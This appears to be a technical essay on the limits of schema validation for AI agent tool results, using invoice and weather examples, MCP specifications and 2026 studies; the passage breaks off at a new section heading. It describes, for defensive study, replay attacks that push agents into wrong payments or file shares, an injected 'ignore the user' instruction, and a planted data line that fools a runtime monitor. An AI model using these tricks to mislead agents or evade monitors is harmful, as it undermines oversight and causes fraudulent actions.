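# What schema validation cannot prove about the results an AI agent gets from its tools

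## What a schema checks in a tool result, and what it cannot check

An AI agent is a language model that acts through other programs, called tools. A tool might search the web, query a database, or send a payment. After each call, the tool returns data, called the tool result, which the agent uses to choose its next action.

Many applications check a tool result before using it, often by validating it against a schema. A schema lists the fields the data should contain, the type of each field, and the values it may take. Validation catches errors such as a missing amount or a word where a number belongs. It cannot establish whether the result answers the agent's request, comes from the source it names, is still true, or permits the next action. Checking these requires information that the result does not contain.

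### The agent loop and the call id

A language model produces text and runs nothing itself. Anthropic's *How tool use works*, a page in the developer documentation for the company's Claude models, describes the division of labour between model and application as a loop. Slightly simplified, it goes like this:

1. The application sends the model the user's instruction and a list of tools, with a schema for the inputs of each.
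2. The model answers with a tool call, which consists of the name of a tool, the arguments for it and an identifier.
3. The application runs the tool with those arguments.
4. The application sends the tool's output back to the model, along with the conversation so far.
5. The model either proposes a further call, which takes the application back to step 3, or writes its final answer.

OpenAI's *Function calling* describes the same flow for the GPT models. An application has two natural places for a check: after a tool runs but before the model reads the result, and after the model proposes an action but before any program carries it out. The first is sometimes unavailable. Anthropic runs a few tools, including web search, on its own servers and normally feeds their output to the model before the application receives anything.

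A model may propose several calls at once, so each result must repeat the call id, an identifier that links it to its call. Anthropic's *Handle tool calls* documents a format in which the model's call has a unique `id`, and the application copies that value into the result's `tool_use_id` field. OpenAI's `call_id` serves the same purpose. A matching id identifies the call that a result is meant to answer, but it doesn't show that the content is correct. In Anthropic's example, the model requests the weather in San Francisco, and the result is "15 degrees" with the matching id. If a bug in the application had fetched the temperature in San Diego, the id would still match, because the application attaches it and the weather service doesn't have to receive it.

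### What JSON Schema checks

JSON is a text format that writes data as named fields, which hold strings, numbers, true-or-false values, lists or further groups of fields. JSON Schema is a language for describing such data. OpenAI's developers use it to define the inputs of function tools. The *Tools* specification of the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for connecting models to tools, also lets a tool publish a JSON Schema for its results.

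Suppose that an agent in a company's accounts department receives the instruction to pay invoice INV-1042. It first calls a tool named `get_invoice`, and the application checks the result against this schema:

```json
{
  "type": "object",
  "required": ["invoice_number", "supplier", "amount",
               "status", "bank_account", "portal_url"],
  "properties": {
    "invoice_number": { "type": "string", "pattern": "^INV-[0-9]{4}$" },
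    "supplier":       { "type": "string", "minLength": 1 },
    "amount":         { "type": "number", "exclusiveMinimum": 0, "maximum": 50000 },
    "status":         { "enum": ["open", "paid", "disputed"] },
    "bank_account":   { "type": "string", "pattern": "^[A-Z]{2}[0-9]{2}[A-Z0-9]{11,30}$" },
    "portal_url":     { "type": "string", "format": "uri" }
  },
  "additionalProperties": false
}
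```

*JSON Schema Validation* (Wright, Andrews and Hutton, 2020) defines most of these keywords for the 2020-12 version of the language. `type` sets the kind of value. `required` lists the fields that must be present, and `enum` lists the permitted values of a field. `exclusiveMinimum` and `maximum` limit a number, here to more than 0 and at most 50,000 euros. `pattern` holds a regular expression, a compact notation for the form of a string, here requiring the invoice number to be "INV-" followed by four digits. The last line rejects any field that the schema does not name.

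Some schema keywords check less than a newcomer would expect. A `pattern` matches anywhere in a string unless the author anchors it with `^` and `$`, so without them the schema above would accept "void-INV-10423". The range keywords constrain only numbers, so a schema with a `maximum` and no `type` accepts the string "four thousand". The example uses `format` to mark the portal address as a web address, but by default `format` is a note for the application and rejects nothing. A developer can switch on checking, but Wright and colleagues limit the requirement to syntax. They say a validator should not be expected to send an email, connect to an address or otherwise find out whether the thing exists, and they recommend that the application do such semantic validation itself.

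Here is a result that passes, from an invented supplier:

```json
{
  "invoice_number": "INV-1042",
  "supplier": "Brandt Paper",
  "amount": 4180,
  "status": "open",
  "bank_account": "DE89370400440532013000",
  "portal_url": "https://portal.brandt-paper.example"
}
```

### Five results that pass and should not lead to payment

If the application pays whenever the schema accepts the result and the status is "open", each of the following leads to a wrong payment.

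1. The tool returns another invoice. The document has the number INV-1043, the same supplier and an amount of 7,900 euros. A faulty lookup or a mixed-up cache is enough to produce it, without any attacker.
2. Someone has since paid the invoice. The document is the one printed above, and it was correct when the tool read the database on Monday. A colleague paid on Tuesday, and the agent acts on Wednesday.
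3. The reply is a forgery. An attacker who can write to the connection, or to a program between the tool and the agent, sends the document printed above. The accounts system has INV-1042 on file as disputed.
4. The reply is correct and the user may not pay. It comes from the real system and is up to date, but the instruction came from an employee who has permission to read invoices and none to release money.
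5. The amount is correct and the bank account is not. Everything matches the real invoice except `bank_account`, which holds GB29NWBK60161331926819, an account that belongs to a thief.

The fifth document would also pass a stricter format check. International account numbers include two check digits, and code that verifies them would accept the thief's number, because the thief needs a working account. A substituted `portal_url` would pass for similar reasons.

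### The same document in different situations

A better schema would not solve this, because each of the five documents ought to lead to payment in some other situation. The INV-1043 document is the right answer to a request for INV-1043. Monday's document was right on Monday. The forged reply can match, byte for byte, a genuine one sent on a day when the invoice was open. The fourth reply is fine if the finance manager gave the instruction, and the fifth is fine if Brandt Paper has moved to a British bank.

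Any test that reads only the document always gives the same document the same verdict. If that document can arrive in both a good situation and a bad one, the test must either let the bad payment through or block the good one. A longer schema can reject more documents, but it cannot distinguish two situations that produce the same document.

Dusseault, Wright and Andrews (2026) include a rule close to this limit in *JSON Schema*, a draft standard they are preparing for the Internet Engineering Task Force, which publishes technical standards for the internet. The July draft requires every validator to give equivalent JSON values the same result. It also forbids a keyword to accept or reject input based on "third factors", meaning anything besides the schema and the input. They write that an "outside verification" scheme could still query external data, but that such schemes are outside the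 document's scope. The August revision keeps the rule, but it is still a draft that they do not consider ready for adoption. The assertion keywords of the 2020-12 version already fit the rule, since each compares the input with values written in the schema.

JSON Schema's standard keywords cannot check that an invoice total equals the sum of its lines because, as Dusseault and colleagues note, most keywords work without looking up data elsewhere in the same document. The argument does not depend on this weakness. Ordinary code can check the sum, and the check is worth having, but it still tests only the document and fails on all five cases.

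What would separate the situations is more input. The extra input differs from question to question:

| Question | What the answer depends on | In the invoice example |
|---|---|---|
| Validity: does the document have the right form? | Document and schema | Six fields, each of the declared type |
| Binding: does the result concern this request? | Document and request | The agent asked for INV-1042 |
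| Freshness: is the result recent enough to use? | Document and time | The payment on Tuesday |
| Source: did the system it names produce it? | Document, and a key or a trusted channel | The accounts system, or someone on the connection |
| Authorization: may this user do this? | Principal, action and policy | An employee without permission to release money |

A principal is the authenticated user or system on whose behalf the agent makes the request. In the last row, the document matters only because it supplies details of the action, such as the amount and the payee, so even a perfect invoice doesn't show that a particular employee is authorized to pay it.

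The answers are also largely independent of one another. The accounts system can send a genuine reply about the wrong invoice, or a genuine reply that is three days old. Whether a check of the source catches the substituted account number depends on how the attacker changed it. If the attacker altered the reply on its way, the check catches it. If the attacker sent the company a false notice of new bank details and a clerk typed them into the supplier record, the check passes, because the accounts system did produce the reply. The application then also needs to know who supplied the account number itself, because it is a protected field, meaning one that selects, permits or directs the effect of an action.

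#### Objections from cleverer schemas

An application could write a new schema for every call, using the keyword `const` to fix the invoice number to "INV-1042". This is sensible and catches the first of the five results, because copying the request into the schema gives the test the second input that binding requires. But the application can fix only values it already knows. It cannot fix the amount or the status, which the agent called the tool to learn, so the schema would still accept a document with the number INV-1042 and the amount of INV-1043. The application could also fix the bank account from a verified list of suppliers' accounts, but the protection would then come from the list.

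A schema can also require a time of issue, the name of the requesting user and an approval, and check the form of each. But no standard keyword compares the time of issue with the current time, and whoever forges the document can fill in these fields too.

*Improving tool-call reliability with JSON Schema 2020-12* (Caldeira, 2026) describes a banking demonstration that shows the uses and limits of such a rule. It concerns the arguments an agent sends to a tool, but the same logic applies to results. The schema requires an approval code for any transfer above 10,000 dollars, and the agent tried to transfer 12,500 dollars without one. The server with the strict schema returned an error saying that the field was missing, and the agent copied the code from its instructions and succeeded on the second attempt. A server that mentioned the rule only in a description returned "transfer rejected",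 which gave the agent no indication of what to fix. Caldeira explains that he withheld the code from the first call because capable models often include it at once, so the contrast is partly staged. Still, the gain in reliability is plausible, since an error that names the missing field is easier to correct.

A schema can require an approval code, but approval depends on people and policy, so the server has to look up whether anyone approved the transfer. The approval code in the demonstration is a constant that anyone can read in the published schema. Caldeira calls it a placeholder and writes that in production the server would verify the authorization decision. His ledger, the program that records transfers, also refuses illegal ones regardless of which schema the agent encountered.

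Digital signatures are an exception to the claim that a schema can do nothing about source. Someone could define a custom keyword that contains the accounts system's public key and verifies a signature inside the document, though the standard vocabulary has no such keyword. It would stop a forger who lacks the private key, and it would seem to respect the rule against third factors because it would read only the schema and the input. The general argument still holds, because someone must establish outside the document that the public key belongs to the accounts system and that the private key hasn't been stolen. A copy of an old signed reply would also pass, because it is the same document as the original.

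Replacing the validator with a language model does not help much either. The model has the user's request and may well detect that INV-1043 is the wrong invoice, which a fixed schema cannot do. But however capable the model is, it has no information about Tuesday's payment or the employee's permissions unless a program supplies it.

### Digests, authentication codes, signatures and nonces

Four cryptographic devices recur in the checks that do address these questions. Each establishes something narrow.

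A digest is a short fingerprint of data that anyone can compute with a cryptographic hash function. Changing one digit of the bank account number on an invoice changes the digest, and nobody can feasibly construct a different document with the same digest. If the digest arrives by a trusted route, the recipient can therefore use it to check that the document hasn't changed since the digest was computed. The digest does not show who wrote the document. If it is sent with the invoice, an attacker who changes the account number can compute a new digest and send that instead.

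A message authentication code, or MAC, is a tag that only holders of a shared secret key can compute or check. A valid MAC shows that some holder of the key produced the message and that nobody has altered it since. According to the entry *message authentication code (MAC)* in the glossary of the US National Institute of Standards and Technology, a MAC does not provide non-repudiation. For example, a company that receives a tagged invoice holds the same key as the sender and could have made the tag itself, so the tag cannot prove to an outside auditor that the sender made it.

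A digital signature is a tag that its owner makes with a private key and that anyone can check with the matching public key. According to NIST's *digital signature*, a properly implemented signature lets others verify the data's origin, its integrity, and that the signatory cannot disown it. NIST's *non-repudiation* describes this last property as proof to a third party that the data came from the holder of the private key. The mathematics does not identify that holder, so Barker, in *Recommendation for Obtaining Assurances for Digital Signature Applications*, asks for separate assurance of the key owner's identity and of the owner's possession of the private key. A signature also does not make the signed statement true. If a clerk has typed the thief's account into the supplier record, the accounts system will sign a result that gives that account as the supplier's.

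A nonce is a value that a protocol uses only once, so that the receiver can recognise a repeated message. The definitions in NIST's *nonce* allow a random number, a timestamp or a sequence number. The value need not be secret, and only some uses require it to be unpredictable. Typically, the application sends a new nonce with its request, and the accounts system includes it in the data that its MAC or signature covers. An old reply then fails the check because it contains an old nonce. This prevents replay, in which someone presents a once genuine message later or in another setting.

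Like a nonce, a call id is unique to its call, but in the loop described above the application, not the tool, attaches it to the result, and no MAC or signature covers it. Without a MAC or signature, even a true nonce gives little protection, because a forger who sees the request can copy the nonce into the reply. Even with a signature, a nonce shows only that the message is new, not that its data is current. For example, an accounts system might read Monday's record of an unpaid invoice from a cache on Wednesday, add Wednesday's nonce and sign the whole message. The message would be new and its signature valid, even if the company had paid the invoice on Tuesday.

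## The output schema of the Model Context Protocol

MCP standardises how an application finds and calls tools that other people have written. A server is a program that offers tools, such as a weather service or an accounts system. A client is the part of the agent's application that communicates with a server. The client sends a `tools/list` request and receives the name, description and input schema of each tool. When the model proposes a call, the client sends a `tools/call` request with the tool's name and arguments, and the server returns a result.

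The specification of 28 July 2026 gives a tool result two fields for data. `content` holds text, images and similar items, and `structuredContent` holds JSON that a program can process directly. A tool may publish an `outputSchema`, a JSON Schema for its `structuredContent`. The client receives this schema with the tool list, before it makes any call.

### Who must check what

Two rules of the Model Context Protocol specification apply to a tool with an output schema:

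- The server MUST return structured results that conform to the schema.
- The client SHOULD validate those results against it.

In internet standards, MUST marks an absolute requirement, while SHOULD marks a recommendation that a developer may set aside for a good reason. Client validation is a SHOULD in the specification, so a client that never looks at the output schema can still comply. The schema is also optional.

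The server's developer writes the schema, so validation shows only whether a result matches the developer's own description. Even when the client does everything right, validation doesn't show whether the schema includes the information the client needs.

The check is still useful within that limit. Model Context Protocol's *Structured Output*, a documentation page for the official Python library, describes a weather tool declared to return a temperature, a humidity and a description of conditions. The tool passes on data from an outside service. The library validates every result before it leaves the server, so when the service stops sending the humidity, the call fails and the model receives an error instead of an incomplete reading. The developer can find the name of the missing field in the server's log. Faults like this are common with outside services, and the check takes the developer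 almost no work, because the library derives the schema from the return type in the tool's code. But if the tool returns an object whose class has no type annotations, the library gives no warning, publishes no schema and checks nothing.

### What SEP-2106 changed

Earlier revisions allowed only a small part of JSON Schema in output schemas. An output schema had to describe an object, with `properties` and `required` as its only other top-level keywords, and `structuredContent` had to be an object too. A tool that returned a list of hourly forecasts therefore had to wrap the list in an object. McBride and Hungerford (2026) proposed lifting these limits in *Tools inputSchema & outputSchema Conform to JSON Schema 2020-12* (SEP-2106), which is part of the July specification.

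Input and output schemas may now use any keyword of JSON Schema 2020-12, though input schemas must still describe an object. `structuredContent` may be any JSON value, including a list, a single number or `null`. Developers can therefore write more precise rules about form, such as using `if` and `then` to require an error code whenever the status is "failed".

The larger vocabulary also gives a hostile server more ways to attack a client. The keyword `$ref` refers to another schema, possibly at a web address, and a client that fetched every such address could request pages inside its own company's network. McBride and Hungerford therefore forbid automatic fetching from the network. They also recommend limiting a schema's depth or the time spent validating it.

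The keywords that SEP-2106 adds still test only the document, so they improve only the check of its form. McBride and Hungerford write that implementations MUST validate all inputs and outputs, but SEP-2106 left the specification's requirement for clients at SHOULD.

### Whether anyone validates the result the model reads

A client can validate structured data only if the server sends some. *Structured Content vs Content*, a survey from June 2026, examined the code of 22 popular open-source servers. Three sent `structuredContent` and eighteen sent only `content`. For the remaining server, from the database company Supabase, the developers had written output schemas, but a shared library removed them before they reached the client. The servers were chosen partly to show different practices, so these numbers are a poor estimate of the share among all servers, but they do show that well-known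 servers often give a client nothing to validate. If a complaint on Apple's developer forum, *Xcode 26.3 MCP server output missing structuredContent*, is right, the MCP server in Apple's programming environment broke the rule by declaring an output schema and then returning no structured data.

A companion survey, also titled *Structured Content vs Content*, found that ten of 19 code paths in open-source clients gave the model only the `content` text. If a server puts 22.5 degrees in `structuredContent` and 31 degrees in the text, such a client could validate the first number and then show the model the second. The specification recommends that servers repeat the structured data as text, but this doesn't protect a client from a faulty server. A safer design is to validate the structured data and then generate the model's text from it. Four of the 19 paths give the model the structured data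 instead of the text, although the survey did not examine whether they validate it.

### Repairing the weather example

The specification illustrates output schemas with a tool named `get_weather_data`. Its only argument is a location, given as a city name or zip code. The output schema requires a number for the temperature, a string for the conditions and a number for the humidity. The example result contains this data:

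```json
{ "temperature": 22.5, "conditions": "Partly cloudy", "humidity": 65 }
```

If the agent asked about New York and the server returned a reading from Tokyo, the result would pass, because the schema requires no place, time or source. A simpler example on the same page returns plain text that names New York and gives the temperature in Fahrenheit, but the structured version omits both the place and the unit. Celsius appears only in a `description` in the schema, which validators ignore, so a temperature of 72 from a server that works in Fahrenheit would pass too. Humidity is also ambiguous, because the specification's example uses a percentage while the Python library's documentation uses a fraction between 0 and 1. A value of 0.83 fits both schemas, but it means 0.83% in the first and 83% in the second.

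The most obvious repair is a required `location` field, which the client compares with the location it asked for. A reading labelled "Tokyo" would then fail the check when the client asked for New York. Both sides have to write places in the same way, since a server might reply "New York, NY" to a request for "New York" or for a zip code. If the server copies the label from the request, as many developers would have it do, a match shows only that the reply contains the requested name, not that the reading came from that place. When a mixed-up cache returns Tokyo's reading, the server labels it "New York" and the comparison succeeds.

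A station identifier, such as KNYC for Central Park in New York or RJTT for Haneda airport in Tokyo, can tie a reading to its location if the server copies the identifier from the stored reading. If the server returns the Haneda reading for New York by mistake, the client rejects it because RJTT isn't on its list of New York stations. This check catches lookup mistakes, but not a dishonest server that attaches KNYC to another temperature, or someone who alters the reply in transit. To guard against those, the client would need a signature that covers the station code and the reading together.

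A reading from last January could still have the right place and station. The server therefore also returns `observed_at`, the time of the measurement. The client compares it with its own clock and a freshness window, the maximum age at which it may still use a result. This value too must come from the stored reading, because if the server fills in the time of its reply, every old reading looks new. MCP's cache lifetimes can't replace this check because they limit how long a client may keep an answer but don't show when the measurement was taken.

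The repaired schema requires the three new fields and can check their form. The comparisons need ordinary code:

```python
def check_reading(request, result, now):
    place = request["location"]
    if result["location"] != place:
        raise ValueError("result names another place")
    if result["station_id"] not in STATIONS[place]:
        raise ValueError("station is not in this place")
    age = now - datetime.fromisoformat(result["observed_at"])
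    if not timedelta(0) <= age <= timedelta(hours=1):
        raise ValueError("reading is too old or dated in the future")
```

Besides the result, the function uses the request, a list of stations, the current time and a limit of one hour. The server supplies none of these four inputs. If it supplied the list of stations, a faulty server could list RJTT as a New York station.

In the specification's shopping basket example, one tool creates a basket and returns the identifier `bsk_a1b2c3`, which the model repeats in later calls because MCP keeps no session to connect them. A schema can check that the identifier is a string, but not whether the caller owns the basket. The specification describes such an identifier as a name and not a capability, and advises servers that authenticate their callers to check the caller's authorization on every call. On a server without authentication, anyone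 who knows the identifier can use the basket, so the specification recommends a hard-to-guess value with a limited lifetime.

### A new schema for each call

The best objection to all this is that a schema written for each call, like the one that fixed the invoice number with `const`, can do part of the work of `check_reading`. For the New York request the client could use:

```json
{
  "type": "object",
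  "required": ["location", "station_id"],
  "properties": {
    "location":   { "const": "New York" },
    "station_id": { "enum": ["KNYC", "KLGA", "KJFK"] }
  }
}
```

The client has to write this schema and apply it in addition to the server's, because the server publishes its output schema before it receives the agent's call, which names the city.

The first two lines inside the braces are easy to leave out, but without them the schema would accept results it should reject. The keywords under `properties` apply only to fields that are present, so without `required` a result that names no place would pass. Both `required` and `properties` apply only to objects, so without `"type": "object"` the schema would accept a list of Tokyo readings, and servers have been allowed to return lists since SEP-2106.

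Written correctly, this is a real binding check. It rejects every result that does not name New York and one of the three stations. It also has practical advantages over custom code, since the client can use its existing validator and store the schema with the result for a later audit. But like the first two comparisons in the Python function, it proves only that the server returned the expected values. A server that copies the location from the request and fills in the station the same way will pass with any reading, and so will a forger who can see the request and knows a New York station.

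Time is harder to handle because no standard keyword compares dates. If a tool gave the time as a number of seconds, the client could enforce an age limit by calculating the oldest acceptable value just before the call and writing it into the schema as a `minimum`. However, the schema would contain only a fixed number that the client's code had calculated from the clock. If the client reused the schema an hour later, a one-hour limit would have become a two-hour limit.

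Standard schema keywords cannot compare two fields that the server fills in, such as an invoice's total and its lines. A weather report might give a station code at the top and another beside each reading. If the client knows the station in advance, it can use `const` to require that code in both places. Otherwise, a report headed with one station's code could contain readings from another and still pass validation.

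### How often valid data is wrong

Two studies from 2026 measured how often data with a valid form has incorrect values. In *Schema-Validated LLM Workflows*, Shapiro, Al-Khatib and colleagues (2026) studied data written by a language model, which differs from a tool result but goes through the same kind of validation. They gave OpenAI's gpt-4o-mini 300 invented business tasks. In 100 of them, the model extracted fields from invoices and complaints. In the rest, it wrote database queries, summarised reports, answered questions about company policy or routed support requests, with 50 tasks of each type.

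Six Python implementations ran every task three times, for a total of 5,400 runs. Five used libraries for building agents or other model programs, including PydanticAI and LangGraph, and one used only the model provider's library. Code then tested each output against the schema and separately scored its content from 0 to 1.

| Task | Runs | Valid under the schema | Valid, but content scored below 0.99 |
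|---|---|---|---|
| Extracting fields | 1,800 | 1,194 | 642 (54%) |
| Policy questions | 900 | 609 | 370 (61%) |
| Routing requests | 900 | 551 | 175 (32%) |
| Database queries | 900 | 600 | 94 (16%) |
| Summaries | 900 | 737 | 9 (1%) |

Altogether, 1,290 of the 3,691 valid outputs, or 35%, scored below 0.99. This threshold is strict because the extraction score is an average over fields, so one wrong field is enough to fall below it. The average score on extraction with PydanticAI was 0.92. Automatic rules produced the scores, and no person has confirmed the apparent errors. The 35% is therefore closer to the share of valid outputs with at least one suspected defect than to the share that are useless, although one wrong field can be enough to make an output useless for a payment.

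The comparison between implementations is less convincing. PydanticAI and LangGraph produced valid data in every run, while the plain library did so in only 38.8% of runs. In a smaller trial by the same team, the plain library also reached 100%, and Shapiro and colleagues don't explain the difference. On three of the five task types, its rate in the main experiment was 33.3%. With three repetitions per task, that rate would be consistent with a technical fault in two of the repetitions, though the paper reports none. The separation between form and content doesn't depend on these doubtful runs, because the three implementations with near-perfect validity still had average scores between 0.91 and 0.94.

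### What an agent does with the right answer to the wrong question

Gurram (2026), in *Measuring What Tool-Using LLM Agents Actually Do*, traced a single wrong value through the work of agents that used simulated weather, calendar and medical tools. After the model wrote its first tool call, Gurram's program changed one argument to a wrong value that was still valid under the schema, such as Manchester instead of London or another patient's number. The tool then returned a correct answer about the wrong city or patient, much like the Tokyo reading above. The model could notice the mistake only from the result.

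Gurram compared each altered run with an unaltered run of the same task by the same model. The simulated tools always give the same output for the same arguments, so code could recalculate the right answer without a human or model judge. Across 1,085 pairs from seven models, the share of wrong outcomes was 52.4% in the unaltered runs and 74.5% in the altered runs.

This average includes many runs in which the agent never made a working call, so the altered value could do no harm. In the 376 pairs where the agent in the altered run made at least one call and every call passed validation, the error rate rose from 26.3% to 71.0%. Of the 277 tasks in this group that agents solved without the alteration, they failed 186 with it. Gurram treats the larger effect as descriptive rather than causal, because the pairs were selected by what happened after the alteration.

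The agents rarely recovered. Across all pairs, 286 tasks changed from right to wrong, and in 157 of them the main failure was that the agent never repeated the call with the correct value. A simple monitor didn't help either. Its rule for stopping the agent at the second validation or tool error triggered in 3.2% of the altered runs and 3.5% of the normal ones. The rates were similar, as expected, because a valid argument causes no error.

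GPT-4o-mini wrote at least one call that failed validation in 79 of its 175 altered runs, and validation kept any wrong values in those calls from reaching a tool. As a result, its error rate barely changed in the altered runs. That is hardly evidence that the agent is robust, because its error rate was already 66.9% without any alteration.

These effects may not be the same size in current systems. Gurram's program caused extra errors by not showing the models the tools' input schemas, and all seven models date from April 2025 or earlier. A newer model might be more likely to notice that a weather report is for Manchester.

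The source of the `const` value also matters in this experiment. Suppose every result named its city. A schema built from the altered call would require Manchester and accept the result, while one built from the model's original call would require London and reject it. If the model had misread the user and written Manchester, the client would need to take the city from the user's request, which is harder when the request is free text. Gurram suggests checking the arguments of each executed call against the city or patient in the user's query. When Gurram tried this on recorded runs, it separated altered runs from normal ones, but partly because of how the experiment was built.

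## An experiment with replayed tool results

Gurram changed the agent's request and let the tool answer it correctly. An agent can also make a correct request and still act on the wrong result if the software around it delivers a genuine result to the wrong task or at the wrong time. This can happen when an application stores tool results in a cache to avoid repeated calls, in a recovery system to restore work after a crash, or in a queue to pass them to a later step. In *TRAP*, Zhi, Zhang and colleagues (2026) tested what agents do when this happens.

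### How the experiment works

The basic test uses two tasks. In task A of an email scenario, the agent has to verify `attachment_A.docx` without sending it. The verification tool returns a result containing `"approved": true` and `"object_id": "attachment-A"`. In task B, the agent has to verify attachment B and send it, but it also receives the result from task A. If the agent sends attachment A, a separate checking program records an error.

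The threat model covers only replays, which can put a stored result in the wrong place but cannot change a field or add an instruction. The tools and the systems they act on are simulated.

Zhi and colleagues built a benchmark with 19 scenarios, including payments, prescriptions and software releases. It has four templates for what can go wrong:

- **Cross-task replay:** the result concerns another object and comes from another task, as in the email example.
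- **Stale-context replay:** the result concerns the right object, but its authorization or another relevant fact has since changed.
- **Duplicate-effect replay:** the result concerns the right object, but the action it supports has already taken effect.
- **Out-of-order replay:** the result concerns the right object but arrives at the wrong point in the workflow, for example after a cancellation.

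A stored result can reach the agent from a recovery database, a message queue or a saved session. The experiment uses a simple version of each mechanism, not a copy of a production system.

Most settings had ten trials. For each setting, the researchers calculated four rates:

- **DAR:** how often the replayed result reached the agent.
- **WAR:** how often the agent then proposed the wrong action.
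- **AAR:** how often the tool gateway, the program through which the agent's calls and results pass, accepted that action.
- **FSER**, the final-state error rate: how often the simulated system ended in a wrong state.

The researchers left out trials in which the model provider blocked the request, the model returned nothing, or the infrastructure failed. Counting those trials as successful defences would have made the agents look safer.

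### Why a schema check and a signature check both pass

A replayed result is the same document that the tool originally returned, so the schema accepts it again, and a signature that covers only the result is still valid. The program in the experiment made a similar integrity check by comparing a stored result's digest with that of the original before delivering it. An unchanged result passes this check however old it is.

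A signature would expose the replay only if it also covered a nonce or a digest of the request, and the recipient checked that value against its pending request.

### Error rates without a defence

The main evaluation tested cross-task replay on eight models released between April and September 2026. It covered seven scenarios and three libraries for building agents: LangGraph, LlamaIndex and the OpenAI Agents SDK.

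| Model | Mean final-state error rate |
|---|---|
| DeepSeek-V4-Pro | 96.7% |
| Gemini-3.8-Flash | 94.3% |
| GPT-5.5 | 87.6% |
| GPT-5.6-Luna | 84.3% |
| GLM-5.3 | 71.9% |
| GPT-5.6-Sol | 61.0% |
| Qwen3.8-Max | 21.9% |
| Claude-Opus-5 | 1.9% |

The mean error rate over all settings was 64.9%. The choice of model accounted for about 74% of the variation in error rates, and the choice of library for less than 1%. Replayed results almost always reached the agent, and without a defence the gateway rarely stopped a wrong action, so the outcome depended mostly on whether the model proposed one.

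These rates are probably higher than they would be with clearer instructions. In the prompt that Zhi and colleagues print for an email case, the agent must verify attachment B first, but if the verification is still running and the session already shows an approved object, the agent may act on that object. An agent that sends attachment A is arguably following its instructions. The comparison between models is still informative, but 64.9% is a poor estimate of how often agents would fail in ordinary use.

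The models found it harder to reject replayed results that concerned the right object. In the file-sharing scenario, Zhi and colleagues tested the other three templates on all 24 combinations of model and library. Stale-context replay caused an error in every trial for 22 combinations, and duplicate-effect and out-of-order replay each did so for 21. Qwen3.8-Max had rejected every cross-task replay in this scenario, although it made errors in 7% of 30 trials in a longer run of that test. It failed every trial of the other three templates.

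GPT-5.5 with LlamaIndex completed the whole benchmark. Its mean error rate was 95.4% under cross-task replay and 100% in each of the 171 settings that used the other templates. The result named the right object and contained a real approval, so it probably gave the model little sign of a problem, and the gateway had no check that could detect one.

A defence against prompt injection, in which an attacker hides instructions in data that the agent reads, might not catch a replay. Zhi and colleagues compared a replayed result with the same result plus an instruction to ignore the user and act on task A's object. In both email and file sharing, DeepSeek-V4-Pro made an error in every trial with the unmodified result and none with the added instruction. In the email case that they examined closely, the model identified the added instruction and refused it, but the unmodified replay contained no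 instruction for it to notice.

### Telling the agent that an approval is no longer valid

If the model lacks information, an obvious remedy is to supply it. Zhi and colleagues tried this with GPT-5.5 and LlamaIndex in the file-sharing scenario, replaying an approval from another task under three conditions:

| Condition | Final-state error rate |
|---|---|
| Nothing has changed | 100% |
| The state of the file has changed, with no notice about the approval | 100% |
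| A notice tells the agent that the approval is revoked | 20% |

The notice clearly helped. In one run the model wrote that the authorization was currently revoked and took no action. In another it received a similar notice but shared the file `policy-draft` without mentioning it. At the study's usual ten trials per setting, a 20% error rate means two errors, which is compatible with a true rate between about 6% and 51%.

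Information about age helped less. The agent could see fields for the result's age, epoch and version in some trials but not in others. For fresh and moderately old results, the error rate was 100% either way. For very old results, showing the fields reduced it from 100% (ten errors) to 60% (six errors), a difference small enough that it might be chance.

The gateway would have accepted the wrong action in all these tests, so safety depended on the model reading and applying the notice. That is weak protection when someone has revoked an approval. The gateway can look up the revocation itself and refuse the action, whatever the model proposes.

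### Three checks at the gateway

Zhi and colleagues tested three defences that work in the gateway and leave the model's prompt unchanged. They used GPT-5.5 with LlamaIndex, with cross-task replay in the email and file-sharing scenarios and the other templates in file sharing only. Without a defence, the error rate in these five settings ranged from 70% to 100%. Each defence reduced it to zero in all five, but they intervened at different points:

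| Defence | Replayed result reached the agent | Agent proposed the wrong action | Gateway accepted it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Call-id matching | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| One-shot ticket | 100% | 90–100% | 0% |
| World-state epoch | 100% | 80–100% | 0% |

The difference matters when the result is confidential. A ticket or an epoch can stop a wrong payment, but by then the agent has read the replayed result and might repeat another customer's data in its answer. The final-state error rate doesn't count that harm because it doesn't change anything in the simulated system.

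A defence could also reach zero errors by blocking everything. To rule this out, the researchers followed each attack with a second phase in which the agent could obtain a new result and complete a legitimate action. No defence blocked a legitimate action, and the agent completed the task in every counted trial. However, the researchers excluded trials in which the second phase did not finish, so a defence that sometimes left the agent stuck might not show up in these figures.

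#### Matching the call id

Call-id matching happens before the model reads the result:

1. When the agent calls a tool, the gateway stores the call id as pending for the current task.
2. When a result arrives, the gateway compares the id attached to it with the pending one.
3. If the ids match, the gateway passes the result to the model. Otherwise it withholds the result.

In the email example, task A's result has the id of a call made in task A, so the gateway withholds it from task B. If the gateway also removes an id from its pending list once the result arrives, it will withhold a second copy of the same result too.

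In *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents*, Kekatos, Lekidis and colleagues (2026) tested a monitor, a program that checks an agent's log against rules, on recorded agent runs. One rule flagged a bank transfer unless the payee had appeared earlier in account data. Another flagged an email unless the recipient had appeared in a directory. In each flagged run, the researchers then planted a line that looked like account or directory data and named the attacker's recipient. With the line added, the monitor accepted the recipient in 94% of the 403 flagged banking runs and 99% of the 203 flagged email runs.

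Kekatos and colleagues then required the data to come from the answer to a lookup that the agent had actually made. Requiring only that it come from a tool result would not have solved the problem, because the planted line could be in a forged tool result. With the lookup rule, the planted line no longer altered any verdict, and the monitor flagged as many of the original attacks as before. The evidence comes from logs rather than live agents. The researchers note that the rule fails if an attacker can forge a matching lookup or control the tool that answers it.

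Call-id matching works only if the ids are unique. Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026) requires a response to repeat the id of its request, but a new id only has to differ from the ids of the sender's other unanswered requests. A client may therefore reuse an id once the first request has been answered, and a stored reply to that request would match the new one.

Two clients can also use the same id at the same time, which caused a vulnerability in MCP's official TypeScript library. According to GitHub's *GHSA-345P-7CG4-V4C7* (2026), the library's clients numbered their requests from 0, and the server kept a list that linked each number to a connection. If a server shared one connection handler between clients, client B could send its request 0 before the server had answered client A's request 0. B's entry then overwrote A's in the list, and the server sent A's answer to B, which was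 waiting for an answer with the same id.

OSV's *CVE-2026-25536* (2026), an entry in a public vulnerability database, lists versions 1.10.0 to 1.25.3 as affected and rates the severity at 7.1 out of 10. Version 1.26.0 reports an error when a server shares a handler in this way. A gateway that relies on call ids can avoid such collisions by generating a long random id for every call and storing it with the task and session.

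#### A ticket that works once

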